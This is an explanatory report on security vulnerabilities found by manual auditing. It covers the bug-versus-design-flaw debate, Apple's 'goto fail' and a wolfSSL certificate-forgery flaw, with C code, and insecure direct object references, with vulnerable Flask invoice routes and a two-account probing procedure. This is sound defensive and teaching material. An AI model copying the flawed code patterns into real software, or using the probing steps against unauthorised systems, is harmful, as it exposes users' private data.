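# Security vulnerabilities found mainly by expert manual auditing

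## What a security vulnerability is, and how bugs differ from design flaws

A security vulnerability is a fault in a computer system that lets someone break the system's security policy, which is the set of written or unwritten rules about who may do what to which data. For example, a hospital's policy might let patients read only their own records. If a patient can open a stranger's file by changing a number in the web address, the hospital's site has a vulnerability.

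Some vulnerabilities make a program crash or corrupt its memory, and automated tools have become good at triggering and detecting these failures. Others let the program run normally while it does something its owner never meant to allow, so only someone who knows what the owner intended can recognize the fault. For at least two decades, security specialists have held that finding such faults takes a human expert who studies the code and design and works out what an attacker could do with them.

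### Basic terms

*Architectural Risk Analysis*, a chapter of Gary McGraw's textbook on software security (2006), defines a vulnerability as a defect or weakness in procedures, design, implementation or internal controls that someone can use to violate the security policy. McGraw adds that the defective component does not have to be related to security.

A specification states what a program is meant to do, such as "a password-reset link works once and expires after an hour". Much of it usually exists only in people's heads. McGraw describes reviewing an online day-trading system, connected to the stock exchange and the cash-machine network, that had no design document. One person in a company of a hundred knew how the whole system worked, and the reviewers spent most of their first week interviewing him. McGraw jokes that without a specification, a system "can't be wrong, it can only be surprising".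 A reviewer must establish what the owner intended before showing that the program departs from it.

This report refers repeatedly to three ways of looking for vulnerabilities. One is fuzzing, which means running a program on a very large number of generated inputs and watching for signs of failure, usually a crash. For example, a tester might feed an image viewer a million damaged pictures and keep the ones that crash it.

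Static analysis examines code automatically without running it, usually for known patterns or data flows. A scanner can flag every use of gets(), a C function that accepts input of any length. In *Getting Past the Bug Parade* (2008), McGraw recalls that the scanner his company released in 1999 could find only very simple problems like that one, and that false positives (reports of vulnerabilities that aren't real) were a pervasive nuisance.

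In a manual audit, a person examines code, a design or a running system, with or without tools. For example, a reviewer might read through a password-reset page and ask how an outsider could get someone else's reset link. Code can become vulnerable even if nobody changes it, because threats change. Microsoft's *Trustworthy Computing* advised developers to review all old code by hand, partly because programmers had written it when the threats were different.

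### Bugs and flaws

An implementation bug is an error in code whose design is sound. For example, a program might set aside 64 bytes of memory for a name and then copy in whatever the user typed without checking the length. Any bytes past the 64th overwrite neighbouring memory, and an attacker who chooses them carefully can sometimes take over the program. The design, which is to store a short name, is fine, and a line or two of code to check the length fixes the bug.

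Suppose a website lets a user who has forgotten her password enter her account name and an email address, then sends a reset link to that address. An attacker can enter her account name with his own address and use the link to take over her account. The code works as designed, and the link is random and expires on time, but the design lets the requester choose where the link goes instead of using the address already on file. A weakness like this, present even if the code follows the design exactly, is a design flaw. OWASP, a non-profit organisation that publishes a widely used list of web security risks, says in *Insecure Design* that a perfect implementation cannot fix an insecure design because the necessary control was never there.

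The two examples also differ in how easily tools can detect them. A fuzzer that tries long names will probably crash the first program, and a scanner can match the unguarded copy. The reset page produces no failure that a fuzzer can detect, and its code contains no suspicious function for a scanner to match.

McGraw did most to establish this vocabulary. David Crocker's *Bugs and flaws* (2006) quotes in full a message in which McGraw says he introduced the two terms in an article about a software security workshop he had chaired in 2003. He uses "bug" for fairly simple implementation errors that are easy to find and fix, and "flaw" for defects of design or architecture. He drew the distinction because he thought the field was neglecting architecture.

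McGraw's favourite example at the time was the Windows Metafile, a Microsoft image format from the late 1980s that allowed a picture to carry code, which the computer would execute while decoding it. Microsoft had included this feature deliberately. Attackers later used it to install spyware and other malware, on at least a million machines by some experts' estimates. McGraw's March 2006 column *How Flawed Is Microsoft?* argued that the company's heavy spending on security had gone mostly into finding bugs. He rejected a Microsoft spokeswoman's view that nobody could anticipate such a flaw, since someone could have found it by asking what an attacker would do with a picture that runs code.

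### Where "half and half" came from

McGraw has also long maintained that bugs and flaws are about equally common, though there is little evidence behind the figure. The abstract of *Risk analysis in software design* (Verdon and McGraw, 2004) attributes "roughly 50 percent" of security problems to design flaws. The 2006 chapter opens with an unqualified 50%. The Microsoft column puts the ratio at "about half-half" and mentions many conversations on the subject with Michael Howard, a security specialist at Microsoft. In 2008 McGraw said he based the figure on his own experience and Microsoft's.

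He is a little more specific in a quotation on the website of Lattix, a software vendor, where he says that Microsoft had found more than half of the problems in its security push to be architectural, and that data from Cigital, McGraw's consultancy, split 60/40 in favour of architectural flaws. None of these passages includes a sample, a count or a rule for classifying doubtful cases. Cigital also sold architectural reviews, so it would naturally have seen many design problems.

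According to eWeek, another consultancy, @stake, analysed a specific sample of 45 e-business applications, and its chief technology officer, Dan Geer, concluded that most of the problems were in the design. This broadly agrees with McGraw, but it is also a consultant's judgement about clients' software.

Any such ratio also depends on what counts as one vulnerability. OWASP notes in its current list, *The Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Risks* (2025), that manual testers tend to report a vulnerability once however often it recurs in an application, while automated tools report every instance. A design flaw that appears on 400 pages could therefore count as one finding or 400, and that choice could easily outweigh the difference between 50% and 60%. It seems fairest to treat "half" as an experienced practitioner's guess that design problems are common, since it can't support anything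 more precise.

The same concern about neglected architecture led the IEEE Computer Society, a professional association, to launch a Center for Secure Design in 2014. Participants at its first workshop brought flaws from their own design reviews and from outside data. They pooled these flaws and picked the 10 largest groups, according to ADTmag's *Bugs Are Bad, But So Are Flaws* (2014).

Arce, Clark-Fisher and colleagues (2014), in *Avoiding the top 10 software security design flaws*, McGraw among them, turned the piles into advice. As Dark Reading's *10 Common Software Security Design Flaws* lists them, the ten items are:

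1. Never assume trust; earn it or give it.
2. Use authentication that nobody can bypass or tamper with.
3. Authorize after authenticating.
4. Keep data strictly apart from control instructions.
5. Validate all data explicitly.
6. Use cryptography correctly.
7. Identify sensitive data and decide how to handle it.
8. Consider the users.
9. Understand how outside components change the attack surface, meaning the parts of a system that an attacker can reach.
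10. Allow for future changes to objects and actors.

The third item depends on a distinction important to access control, between authentication, which establishes who a user is, and authorization, which decides what that user may do. Arce and colleagues illustrate it with a cash machine. The card and PIN identify the customer, but the machine has to check her withdrawal limit separately.

### One missing check, several labels

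A billing site might have forty pages that display invoices, one of which is missing the check that the invoice belongs to the person requesting it. This can accurately be described as a coding bug or as a design flaw, and the two descriptions lead to different repairs. If it is treated as a bug, one added line fixes it. A reviewer could equally fault the design for relying on developers to remember the check on every page. Arce and colleagues recommend that shared infrastructure carry out authorization checks, which would remove the need to remember them.

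McGraw's peers raised this kind of problem early, in a long argument on the Secure Coding mailing list in February 2006. Crispin Cowan of Novell thought "bug" and "flaw" were synonyms and that McGraw was creating jargon. Chris Wysopal preferred "design defect" and "implementation defect", terms modeled on manufacturing. Crocker replied that the manufacturing model doesn't apply to software, which has no equivalent of a badly cast part. He regarded coding errors as low-level design errors, like choosing a bolt that meets its specification but breaks under load.

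Jeff Williams (2006), in the same thread, made what seems to me the best objection — no, the most useful one.

He argued that requirements, architecture, design and code are all models of the same system, and that a single problem can exist in all of them at once. He saw some value in the label "design flaw" as a warning to a team that it would have to redo the design.

Brian Chess of Fortify, a maker of scanning tools, had heard a flaw defined as code that does what the programmer intended and a bug as something unintended. He doubted that the distinction was useful, since a reviewer who knows the intent learns little else about the defect. He also pointed out that a scanner can easily spot a line of Java that requests a key for DES, an outdated cipher, even though choosing a weak cipher is a design decision.

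McGraw (2006) answered him with the example of an interface that its designers never meant to expose, but that became reachable over time and had no authentication or authorization. McGraw asked how a static analysis tool would find such an error of omission. One possible answer is that a tool can search for interfaces that lack these checks once a person has supplied the policy that every interface needs them.

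Five years later Kevin Wall, a security specialist at the telephone company Qwest, proposed a third category. Often nobody has written down that access to some data requires a particular role, so the developers never think to build the check. Wall could not see how to blame the architecture for the missing check. In *informIT*, a later thread on the same list, McGraw (2011) replied that he would classify errors of omission as ambiguities in the specification, one of his three groups of flaws.

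Other sources also classify vulnerabilities inconsistently. SANS's *Software security starts with software quality*, summarising McGraw's scheme, lists missing authorization as a design flaw. By contrast, *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (Zorz, 2026) reports that an August 2026 review by CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, groups broken access control with memory-safety failures as "avoidable coding errors". McGraw's own classification of SQL injection, in which an attacker enters database commands into an ordinary input field, has changed. He listed it as a bug in 2008, but the 2014 document he co-wrote treats it as a consequence of failing to separate data from instructions.

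McGraw has conceded that bugs and flaws are the ends of a spectrum. It is still useful to ask whether a particular vulnerability would exist in code that followed the design exactly. The overrun buffer would not, but the reset page's vulnerability would. For a missing check, the answer depends on what the design required, and there may be no answer if nobody wrote a design.

### How the catalogues draw the line

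The Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), which the non-profit MITRE maintains, is the standard catalogue of weakness types. It had 968 entries when OWASP prepared its 2025 list. The entries range from broad "pillars" to "variants" tied to a particular language or technology, but these levels of abstraction don't correspond to the distinction between bugs and design flaws.

OWASP introduced a category called Insecure Design in 2021, and it fell from fourth place to sixth in 2025. MITRE's *OWASP Top Ten 2025 Category A06:2025* lists the 39 CWE entries that OWASP assigned to the category. Some are design flaws, such as "Reliance on Untrusted Inputs in a Security Decision", which describes the reset page well. But the category also includes "Function Call with Incorrectly Specified Arguments", which is a plain coding error, and "Use of Potentially Dangerous Function", which is closely related to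 McGraw's gets() example. MITRE cautions that such categories are informal groupings and says it will work with OWASP to improve the mappings.

Much of what Arce and colleagues regard as design falls outside OWASP's Insecure Design category. Broken Access Control, which ranks first on the OWASP list, is a separate category, as are cryptographic failures and authentication failures. OWASP acknowledges that some overlap among its ten categories is practically unavoidable. The split between Insecure Design and the other nine categories therefore can't be used to count design flaws and bugs.

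### Logic flaws

The distinction between logic flaws and low-level errors, such as memory violations, matters more to who finds a vulnerability than the distinction between bugs and design flaws. A logic flaw is a gap between what a program does and what its specification or policy requires, without a low-level error. It can be an implementation bug or a design flaw. The table applies both distinctions to six cases, with the overrun buffer for comparison.

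| Case | Implementation bug or design flaw? | Logic flaw or low-level error? |
|---|---|---|
| Overrun buffer | Implementation bug | Low-level error: the program writes outside the memory set aside |
| Faulty check of a certificate, the file that proves a website's identity | Implementation bug: the design requires a check that the code fails to perform | Logic flaw: the program accepts an impostor |
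| Missing access check | Either, depending on what the design required | Logic flaw: the server hands over another user's data |
| Forged login under single sign-on, where one login serves many sites | Either: one component may be wrong, or the way they fit together | Logic flaw: a site admits the wrong person |
| Attack on a cryptographic protocol | Usually a design flaw: faithful code is still open to attack | Logic flaw: the protocol breaks a promise such as secrecy |
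| Smart contract, a program that holds money on a blockchain | Either, depending on whether the design stated the rule that failed | Logic flaw: the contract releases money it should keep |
| Log4Shell, a vulnerability in a Java logging library | Design flaw: a deliberate feature proved dangerous | Logic flaw: the library acts on instructions in text it should only record |

All six are logic flaws, but their entries in the middle column vary. The certificate check fits poorly into McGraw's scheme, in which tools find bugs and people find flaws, because it is an ordinary coding error that doesn't make the program crash.

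The historical claim is therefore better stated as people finding logic flaws while tools find crashes. Security Magazine's *AI Applications Contain Security Vulnerabilities, According to Report* (2026) relays findings from BreachLock, a penetration-testing company, that insecure design and business logic flaws still don't appear on scanner reports and that finding them takes testers who understand how an application should behave. BreachLock has a commercial interest in that conclusion because it sells such tests, but OWASP, which doesn't, also says its data are largely limited to what the industry can test automatically.

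The claim had exceptions even before language models. McGraw wrote in 2008 that scanning tools could not automate the search for flaws, but in the same article he described custom scanning rules that caught defects resembling flaws as much as bugs. Microsoft lists logic flaws among the things fuzzing can uncover. This is possible if someone gives the fuzzer a test oracle (any way of deciding whether an observed behaviour is correct) that checks for more than crashes. In these cases a person had to specify what counted as wrong. Language models complicate the claim because they can read code alongside its comments and documentation and infer what the program was supposed to do without being told. Results from 2026 have put in doubt whether a person is still needed to specify this.

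## Why a faulty certificate check gives no sign of failure

On 21 February 2014 Apple released a security update for iPhones and iPads. Its advisory, reproduced in the blog post *goto fail* (2014), mentioned only "missing validation steps". By the next day outside programmers had traced the problem to one duplicated line of code, and the vulnerability became known as "goto fail" after that line. It is listed as CVE-2014-1266 in Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE), the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities.

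### Apple's duplicated line

When a browser connects to a bank, the two sides begin with a handshake under TLS (Transport Layer Security, formerly SSL), the protocol that encrypts web traffic. The bank's server sends its certificate, but anyone can copy a certificate, so the server must also prove its identity by signing fresh data with the matching private key. In the connections relevant here, it signs a temporary key that the two sides will use to set up their encryption, and the browser checks the signature.

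ImperialViolet's *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (2014), a blog post by Adam Langley, gives Apple's code for this check. With simpler names, the important lines are:

```c
if ((err = add_to_hash(server_random)) != 0)
    goto fail;
if ((err = add_to_hash(temporary_key)) != 0)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
if ((err = finish_hash(digest)) != 0)
    goto fail;
/* the code that checks the signature comes here */
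fail:
    free_buffers();
    return err;
```

Each step stores a result in `err`, where zero means that nothing went wrong. The instruction `goto fail` jumps to the label near the bottom, where the function tidies up and returns `err`. In C, an `if` without braces controls only the next statement. The duplicated `goto fail` therefore doesn't belong to the `if` above it, although the indentation suggests that it does. An ordinary connection goes as follows:

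1. Both `add_to_hash` steps succeed, so `err` is zero and the program skips the `goto fail` that belongs to each.
2. The program reaches the duplicate, which has no condition attached, and jumps to the end.
3. The function returns zero, and the rest of the program takes this to mean that the signature is valid.

The signature check never runs. An honest server sends a correct signature, so skipping the check has the same result as performing it. Every legitimate website loads as usual, and a test suite that uses only valid connections passes.

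An attacker who controls the network, perhaps by running a café's Wi-Fi, can send the bank's genuine certificate and then sign with any key, or leave the signature out. Certificate pinning makes an app accept only certificates it already knows, but Langley doubted it would have helped, because the attacker sends the genuine certificate. TLS 1.2, the newest version at the time, used a different function without the error, but this gave little protection because an attacker could choose an older version if the victim's device still accepted it.

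According to Bland's *Finding More Than One Worm in the Apple*, the error had been in Apple's software since iOS 6.0 in September 2012. For about 17 months, very large numbers of people used the faulty check every day and had no reason to complain.

### wolfSSL's missing comparison

CVE-2026-5194, a vulnerability in the open-source cryptography library wolfSSL, is harder to see in the code. Billions of devices use wolfSSL, according to Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026). The vulnerability concerns the signature on the certificate itself.

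A certificate authority (CA) issues certificates and signs each one in two steps. It first runs the contents through a hash function, which produces a short digest that changes if anyone alters the contents. It then combines the digest with its private key to make the signature. To check an ECDSA signature, a common type, software recomputes the digest from the certificate it received, treats the digest as a number, and tests whether an equation holds between that number, the signature and the CA's public key.

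Some other signature types, such as Ed25519, include their own hashing, and wolfSSL correctly skips the separate hashing step for them. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-7DG11TPA · wolfssl/wolfssl*, a technical analysis published on 2 June 2026, traces the vulnerability to how the library chose between the two procedures. wolfSSL used a label in the certificate, which a forger can set to anything, to decide whether to hash, and the type of the CA's key to decide which equation to test. The code never checked that the label and the key agreed.

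A certificate labelled Ed25519 but supposedly issued by a CA with an ECDSA key reached the ECDSA test with an empty digest. The test set a maximum digest length but no minimum, and it treated the empty digest as zero. With a digest of zero, the verification equation doesn't depend on the certificate's contents, and anyone who knows the CA's public key can find a signature that satisfies it.

A forger could use this to make a certificate for any website, containing his own key, and vulnerable software would accept it as if a trusted CA had issued it. If he could also divert a victim's traffic, he could pose as her bank. wolfSSL's own description in the official CVE record, MITRE's *wolfSSL ECDSA Certificate Verification* (2026), is milder. It mentions "reduced security" if the attacker knows the CA's public key, but CAs publish those keys, so almost any attacker could meet that condition.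 wolfSSL did rate the vulnerability as critical, with a score of 9.3 out of 10, which is listed in the US government's vulnerability database under NVD's *CVE-2026-5194 Detail* (2026).

The flaw affects versions from 3.12.0 up to, but not including, 5.9.1. A build was vulnerable only if it also had ML-DSA or EdDSA, the family that includes Ed25519, enabled. Anthropic reported the problem on 26 March 2026, and wolfSSL released the fix on 8 April.

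Anthropic credits the discovery to Claude Mythos Preview, a language model that the company says has found thousands of other serious vulnerabilities. Anthropic's analysis of the wolfSSL error doesn't describe the search that led to it, but Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026) describe their usual procedure in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview’s cybersecurity capabilities*. They put a project and its source code on an isolated machine and ask the model, in about a paragraph, to find a vulnerability. The model first rates each file from 1 to 5 by how likely it is to contain one. Separate copies of the model then take one file each, look for possible vulnerabilities in the code, and run the program to test whether they are real. A final copy judges whether each report is correct and worth attention.

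The CVE record lists Nicholas Carlini of Anthropic as the finder and doesn't mention a model, while Anthropic's analysis credits Claude. A tally of human and machine discoveries based on CVE credits would count this one as human, which is wrong or at least debatable.

### The test oracle problem

A test oracle is a function that takes an observed run of a program and returns "pass", "fail" or "undecided". A crash detector returns "fail" if the program crashes and should return "undecided" otherwise, although testers easily mistake the absence of a crash for a pass. On Apple's faulty code, a crash detector would have returned "undecided" for every connection, genuine or forged.

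A crash detector is popular because it needs no knowledge of the program. The same is true of AddressSanitizer, a tool that monitors a running program and reports any use of memory outside the areas set aside for it. No correct C program uses memory this way, whatever its purpose. Carlini and colleagues call the tool a "perfect crash oracle", meaning that its reports are true, although it can't report an error that no test has triggered. When they sent Mozilla 112 Firefox bugs found by an earlier model, all of them proved real. They concede that they lose this near-certainty with logic flaws.

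An authorization rule such as "only the customer and her accountant may open this invoice" belongs to one program, and someone has to supply it. The sources of such a judgement fall into four groups:

- An implicit oracle relies on what is wrong in any program, such as a crash or a memory error.
- A specified oracle comes from a written statement of correct behaviour. wolfSSL had one available, because US government standards set minimum digest lengths for these signatures. It helps only if someone turns the relevant sentence into a test, and only if the specification is itself sound, which can't be taken for granted with cryptographic protocols.
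- A derived oracle uses indirect evidence of what is right, such as an earlier version of the program or another program that does the same job.
- A human oracle is a person who looks at the result and decides. This is the most flexible arrangement and much the slowest. Nobody can inspect a million handshakes.

The release that fixed CVE-2026-5194 gives a rough idea of how much an implicit oracle leaves out. The notice that Solar Designer (2026), in *wolfSSL 5.9.1 CVE and non-CVE fixes*, sent to a security mailing list covers 21 vulnerabilities. Twelve are memory errors, which a tool like AddressSanitizer should report once a test triggers them. In six others the library accepts something it ought to reject, such as a forged signature or a message that an attacker has altered, and there is no memory error for the tool to report. (The remaining three don't fit neatly into either group.)

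Five of the six false acceptances were credited to Anthropic or to Calif.io, a security company working with Claude, compared with two of the twelve memory errors. This is weak evidence, because it covers one release of one library and the credits don't record what tools the other finders used. But it's the reverse of what one would expect if automated methods still found only crashes.

Testing can also fail because nobody tries the right input. Carlini and colleagues describe a 16-year-old memory error in FFmpeg, a widely used video library, that occurs only when a single video frame contains 65,536 slices. A memory-error detector would have reported it immediately, but years of fuzzing had apparently never produced such a frame. With "goto fail", any wrong signature would trigger the bug, and testers lacked only a way to recognise that accepting it was an error. wolfSSL had both problems.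 A tester who changed the label on an ordinary certificate would have seen the library reject it, because the old signature wouldn't satisfy the altered equation. With the label changed, only a signature made specially for an empty digest would be accepted.

One way to confirm a suspected logic flaw is to build the attack. Anthropic reports that Mythos Preview constructed an exploit that would let an attacker forge certificates with the wolfSSL vulnerability. If a library accepts a certificate made without the CA's private key, there is little doubt that its check is faulty. This works well for certificates because everyone agrees on what they are for. It would settle less in a company's internal software, where a successful "attack" might turn out to be an intended feature.

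### Policies that one run can't settle

Both certificate vulnerabilities break a rule that a single run can violate. Software that accepts one forged signature is wrong, whatever it does the rest of the time. Some security policies, such as "Alice learns nothing about Ben's data", are not rules of this kind.

Suppose Alice types Ben's email address into a login page, guesses a password, and gets the reply "wrong password". If the page replies "unknown user" for addresses without an account, the difference tells Alice that Ben has one, even though neither reply is a fault on its own. This could matter a good deal if the site belongs to a clinic.

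To state the policy more exactly, let in(*r*) be everything Alice enters during a run *r*, and out(*r*) everything she sees. For a program without random behaviour, the policy is that for every two possible runs *r*₁ and *r*₂:

if in(*r*₁) = in(*r*₂), then out(*r*₁) = out(*r*₂).

Alice must see the same thing in both runs, even if Ben's data differs between them. Computer scientists call a condition on the whole set of a program's possible runs a hyperproperty. An oracle that examines one run at a time cannot enforce this condition. The run in which Alice sees "wrong password" could come from the leaky site, or from a safe site that gives the same reply whether or not the account exists, so the oracle would either fail the safe site or pass the leaky one.

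The same wolfSSL release fixed a real vulnerability that resembles this. An attacker could submit many altered versions of an encrypted message and work out the original text by comparing the library's responses, each of which revealed very little. Cryptographers call this a "padding oracle", using "oracle" in another sense, for something an attacker can query.

A tester can look for such leaks by running the program twice, changing only Ben's data, and comparing what Alice sees. Clocks and random numbers have to stay the same in both runs, or they will cause differences too. Any remaining difference shows that the program violates the policy, but however many pairs of runs match, an untried pair might still differ. The policy is also too strict for most software. A shop that shows "only one left", for example, deliberately reveals something about other customers' purchases, so someone still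 has to decide which differences are acceptable.

### Substitutes for a missing oracle

Differential testing gives the same input to several programs meant to do the same job and compares their results. It suits certificate checking because several independent libraries follow the same standards. Every library rejects random bytes before reaching the interesting checks, so a tester can instead cut up real certificates and recombine the parts. The resulting files are well formed but contain combinations no CA would issue. If one library accepts a certificate and another rejects it, at least one of them is probably faulty.

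This would have had a good chance of finding CVE-2026-5501, another of the vulnerabilities in the wolfSSL release. An ordinary website's certificate carries a flag meaning that its owner may not issue other certificates. If someone used such a certificate to issue another one anyway, a wolfSSL function that some applications call directly accepted the new certificate without checking its signature, even if the signature was gibberish. Recombined certificates could easily include such a chain, and a correct library would reject it.

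The method would probably have missed CVE-2026-5194, because a recombined certificate wouldn't contain the specially made signature. wolfSSL would have rejected the certificate, as every other library would, but for the wrong reason. Comparing certificate checkers wouldn't have exposed "goto fail" either, because that attack uses genuine certificates and the fault is later in the handshake.

Disagreement between libraries also doesn't show which one is right. One may be too lax, the other may be too strict, or the standard may allow both answers, so a person has to read the standard and decide. Agreement is weak evidence that the libraries are correct, because they can share code or their programmers can misread the standard in the same way.

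Metamorphic testing needs only one program. The tester changes an input in a way that should have a known effect on the result, even without knowing what the correct result was to begin with. Langley's check for "goto fail" can serve as a worked example. He put up a test site that sent the same certificates at two addresses. At one, the server signed the handshake correctly. At the other, it signed with a completely different key. If *h* is the correct handshake and *h*′ is the copy with the wrong key, the relation is:

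if the device accepts *h*, then it must reject *h*′.

A vulnerable iPhone accepted both. This test needs no crash and no access to Apple's code, and it would work on any browser.

For wolfSSL, a natural relation is that if the library accepts a certificate, it must reject a copy with a different website name and the old signature. The vulnerable versions would have passed this test on every ordinary certificate, because they hashed those correctly. They would fail it only if the tester started from a forged certificate of the right kind, in which case she would already have found the vulnerability. Metamorphic testing removes the need to know the right answer for each input, but the tester still has to choose a relation and a starting input that expose the fault.

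Even the simple relation for "goto fail" is laborious to test routinely. Langley wrote on ImperialViolet that testing it takes a separate TLS implementation with many options for sending invalid handshakes. The team behind Chromium, the open-source browser, had such a tool, but he couldn't recall a test for exactly this error. Bland, however, argued that Apple could have restructured the function so that a small test of it alone would catch the mistake. He seems right that the test needn't have taken much work, but someone would still have had to think of testing a bad signature, and programmers naturally spend more time making good connections work.

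### What a compiler could have noticed

"Goto fail" is a slightly awkward example of a fault that only someone who knows what the code is meant to do can see. The duplicated line made the code between it and the `fail` label unreachable, and a compiler (the program that turns source code into something a computer can run) can detect unreachable code without any information about TLS. Unreachable code is suspicious in almost any program, so a warning about it works rather like an implicit oracle applied to the code's text.

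Langley compiled a cut-down version of the error with two common compilers, GCC 4.8.2 and Clang 3.3, using the option `-Wall`, which supposedly turns on all warnings. Neither produced one. A reader told him that Clang did have a warning for unreachable code, but that `-Wall` didn't include it. Langley guessed that in large projects it might produce too many false positives to be worth having. According to *The Apple goto fail vulnerability* (Wheeler, 2014), GCC could once detect such code, but the feature was quietly dropped. Wheeler suggests that a search for duplicated lines might also have helped.

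He also thought code review could be effective, and was confident that either of two colleagues would have caught the mistake if he had made it. This is plausible, since the two identical lines are easy to spot once someone looks at them, but he was judging only two people he knew. Whatever review Apple carried out didn't stop the line from reaching its customers.

The wolfSSL error gave a compiler much less to detect. The code that skipped hashing was correct for Ed25519, and the ECDSA equation was right for an ECDSA key. But the code didn't compare the certificate's label with the CA's key, and no general rule of programming requires those two values to agree.

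## How missing access checks expose other users' data

Any certificate library should reject a forged signature, but no standard covers who may read a particular company's invoices. Each web application has its own access rules, and its programmers have to enforce them on every page that handles private data. The hospital site that let a patient open a stranger's file by changing a number didn't check whether the patient was allowed to see that file. Security specialists call this flaw an insecure direct object reference (IDOR), where an "object" is any stored item, such as an invoice or a user account.

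A closely related term is broken object-level authorization (BOLA). *Broken Object Level Authorization in the Wild* (Kaur, 2026) uses IDOR for the attacker's technique of supplying someone else's identifier, and BOLA for the underlying fault: the server never checks whether the user may use the object. Many people treat the two terms as synonyms.

### An invoice page in three versions

Semgrep's *Can LLMs Detect IDORs?* (2025) contains a useful example, a web page that returns an invoice. Semgrep is a company that sells code-scanning tools. Slightly shortened, the first version is:

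```python
@app.route('/organization/<int:org_id>/invoice/<int:invoice_id>')
def get_invoice(org_id, invoice_id):
    org = Organization.query.get_or_404(org_id)
    invoice = Invoice.query.get_or_404(invoice_id)
    return jsonify(invoice.to_dict())
```

Suppose Alice works for Acme, which is organization 7 and has invoice 1041. Another organization, Birch, has invoice 1042. The site requires users to log in. When Alice visits `/organization/7/invoice/1041`, the site's code looks up the organization and the invoice by number and returns the invoice. It doesn't check whether Alice is allowed to see either record, so she can change 1041 to 1042 and read Birch's invoice. Any logged-in user can read every invoice on the site this way.

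The next version adds a check that the invoice belongs to the organization in the address:

```python
    if invoice.organization_id != org_id:
        return error(404)
```

Now `/organization/7/invoice/1042` fails, because invoice 1042 isn't Acme's. But Alice can also change the 7 to an 8. The two records then match, and she gets Birch's invoice. Any user can still get any invoice by finding the right pair of numbers.

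The last version also checks that the user belongs to the organization:

```python
    if org not in get_current_user().organizations:
        return error(403)
```

Alice can now read only Acme's invoices. Both checks are necessary, because with the membership check alone, she could name her own organization, pass the check, and then request one of Birch's invoices by its number.

| Alice's request | No checks | Invoice check only | Membership check only | Both checks |
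|---|---|---|---|---|
| Organization 7, invoice 1041 | Her own invoice | Her own invoice | Her own invoice | Her own invoice |
| Organization 7, invoice 1042 | Birch's invoice | Refused | Birch's invoice | Refused |
| Organization 8, invoice 1042 | Birch's invoice | Birch's invoice | Refused | Refused |

According to Semgrep (2026), the membership-only mistake recurs in real code. An application checks the user's right to a parent object, then changes a child object that it looked up separately. Reviewers can easily misread this code because it does contain an authorization check.

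Even the last version is correct only if every member of an organization is allowed to read all its invoices. If only owners should have access, Alice, an ordinary member, can still read invoices she shouldn't.

### Why scanners struggle with an absent check

*ABSENTIA* (Duarte, Oke and colleagues, 2026) compares a similar invoice page with SQL injection. A data-flow tool can find an injection by following text from a request into a database command that the text can alter. This is wrong in every application, so one rule per programming language covers it. The invoice page also passes a number from the request into a database lookup, but it has to do this to work.

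The tool lacks the policy, which Duarte and colleagues write as a relation, permitted(*u*, *r*), that holds if user *u* may act on resource *r*. A page is vulnerable if it accepts some request for which permitted(*u*, *r*) is false. The same code can therefore be safe in one application and vulnerable in another. Semgrep illustrates this with two nearly identical pages that look up a user by number and don't check who is asking. The first is an IDOR because it returns the whole record, including a home address and a passport number. The second is fine because it returns only a username and an email address, which the site's owner means to be public.

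A tool also can't reliably detect a missing check by examining only the page's own code. The check may be in a function that the page calls, or in middleware, which is code that the web framework runs automatically before the page. A tool that reported every lookup by number would produce many false positives.

Duarte and colleagues tested two widely used static analysers, CodeQL and Semgrep's scanner, on 30 publicly disclosed access-control vulnerabilities. Semgrep's scanner produced 6,398 findings, but neither tool identified any of the 30. Yang, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *Suspected Until Inspected*, also reported a 0% detection rate for CodeQL on a different set. This result reflects the available rules as much as the method, because CodeQL's ready-made IDOR query is for C# and none of the tested applications were written in it.

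Monitoring traffic doesn't help much either. Barach (2026) points out in *AuthProbe* that a malicious request can look exactly like a legitimate one, which gives a firewall no basis for blocking it. Alice's request for invoice 1042 differs from the one Ben sends every day only in the login attached to it. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, considered fuzzing and static analysis ineffective against these vulnerabilities, though it noted that they are usually easy to exploit by hand.

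### Testing with two accounts

A tester who knows the policy can look for an IDOR with two accounts and a tool for editing web requests:

1. Register Alice and Ben in separate organizations, and create an invoice in each.
2. Log in as Ben, open his invoice, and save the request and the reply.
3. Send the same request with Alice's login. Then try mixed numbers, such as Alice's organization with Ben's invoice.
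4. Compare the replies. If Alice receives Ben's invoice, the page is vulnerable. If the request was to delete the invoice, log in as Ben again and see whether it's still there.

With a single account, the tester can see that another invoice loads but can't confirm whose it is or whether its owner meant to share it.

To test more than one page, the tester needs an access matrix, which sets out what each user may do to each object. Suppose Acme also has an owner, Olga, and only owners may delete invoices. With three users, two actions and two objects, the matrix has 3 × 2 × 2 = 12 cells:

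| User | Read 1041 (Acme) | Delete 1041 (Acme) | Read 1042 (Birch) | Delete 1042 (Birch) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Alice, member of Acme | Yes | No | No | No |
| Olga, owner of Acme | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| Ben, member of Birch | No | No | Yes | No |

Ordinary use of the site covers only the four "yes" cells. Any IDOR will be in one of the eight "no" cells, which people try only when they are testing or attacking the site.

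The number of cells grows quickly. Adding a logged-out visitor, two more actions (editing and sending) and an archived invoice for each company gives 4 users × 4 actions × 4 invoices = 64 cells. The applications that Duarte and colleagues studied had a median of 220 routes, each combining one type of web address with one operation, such as reading or deleting. Testing every route with four users and four objects would take 3,520 requests, not counting those that mix parent and child numbers.

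A script can easily send 3,520 requests, but filling in the "yes" and "no" answers is slower because someone has to supply the policy. Barach's AuthProbe, an automated version of the two-account test, avoids most of this work by assuming that only an object's owner should be able to read it. It takes a machine-readable list of an application's endpoints (the addresses that accept requests), logs in under two or more accounts, and records which objects each one owns. It then tries to read one account's objects from another and compares the result with what the owner receives. The assumption suits job applications, the case Barach had in mind, because they should be private. On a site where users share documents, someone would have to specify which sharing was deliberate.

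### What 84 disclosed reports contain

Kaur studied such faults in reports from HackerOne, a bug bounty platform where companies pay outside researchers for valid vulnerability reports. Kaur searched for reports labelled "IDOR" or "Improper Access Control" from January 2021 to January 2026, took the 200 most upvoted, and classified the 107 that had enough relevant detail. Of these, 84 were cases of BOLA; many of the others described a different problem despite their labels. Kaur sorted the 84 into six families by why authorization failed.

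| Family | Reports | A real example |
|---|---|---|
| Action-level: the attacker changes another user's object | 35 (41.7%) | At Mozilla, an attacker could delete a victim's account by sending the victim's email address from the attacker's own session |
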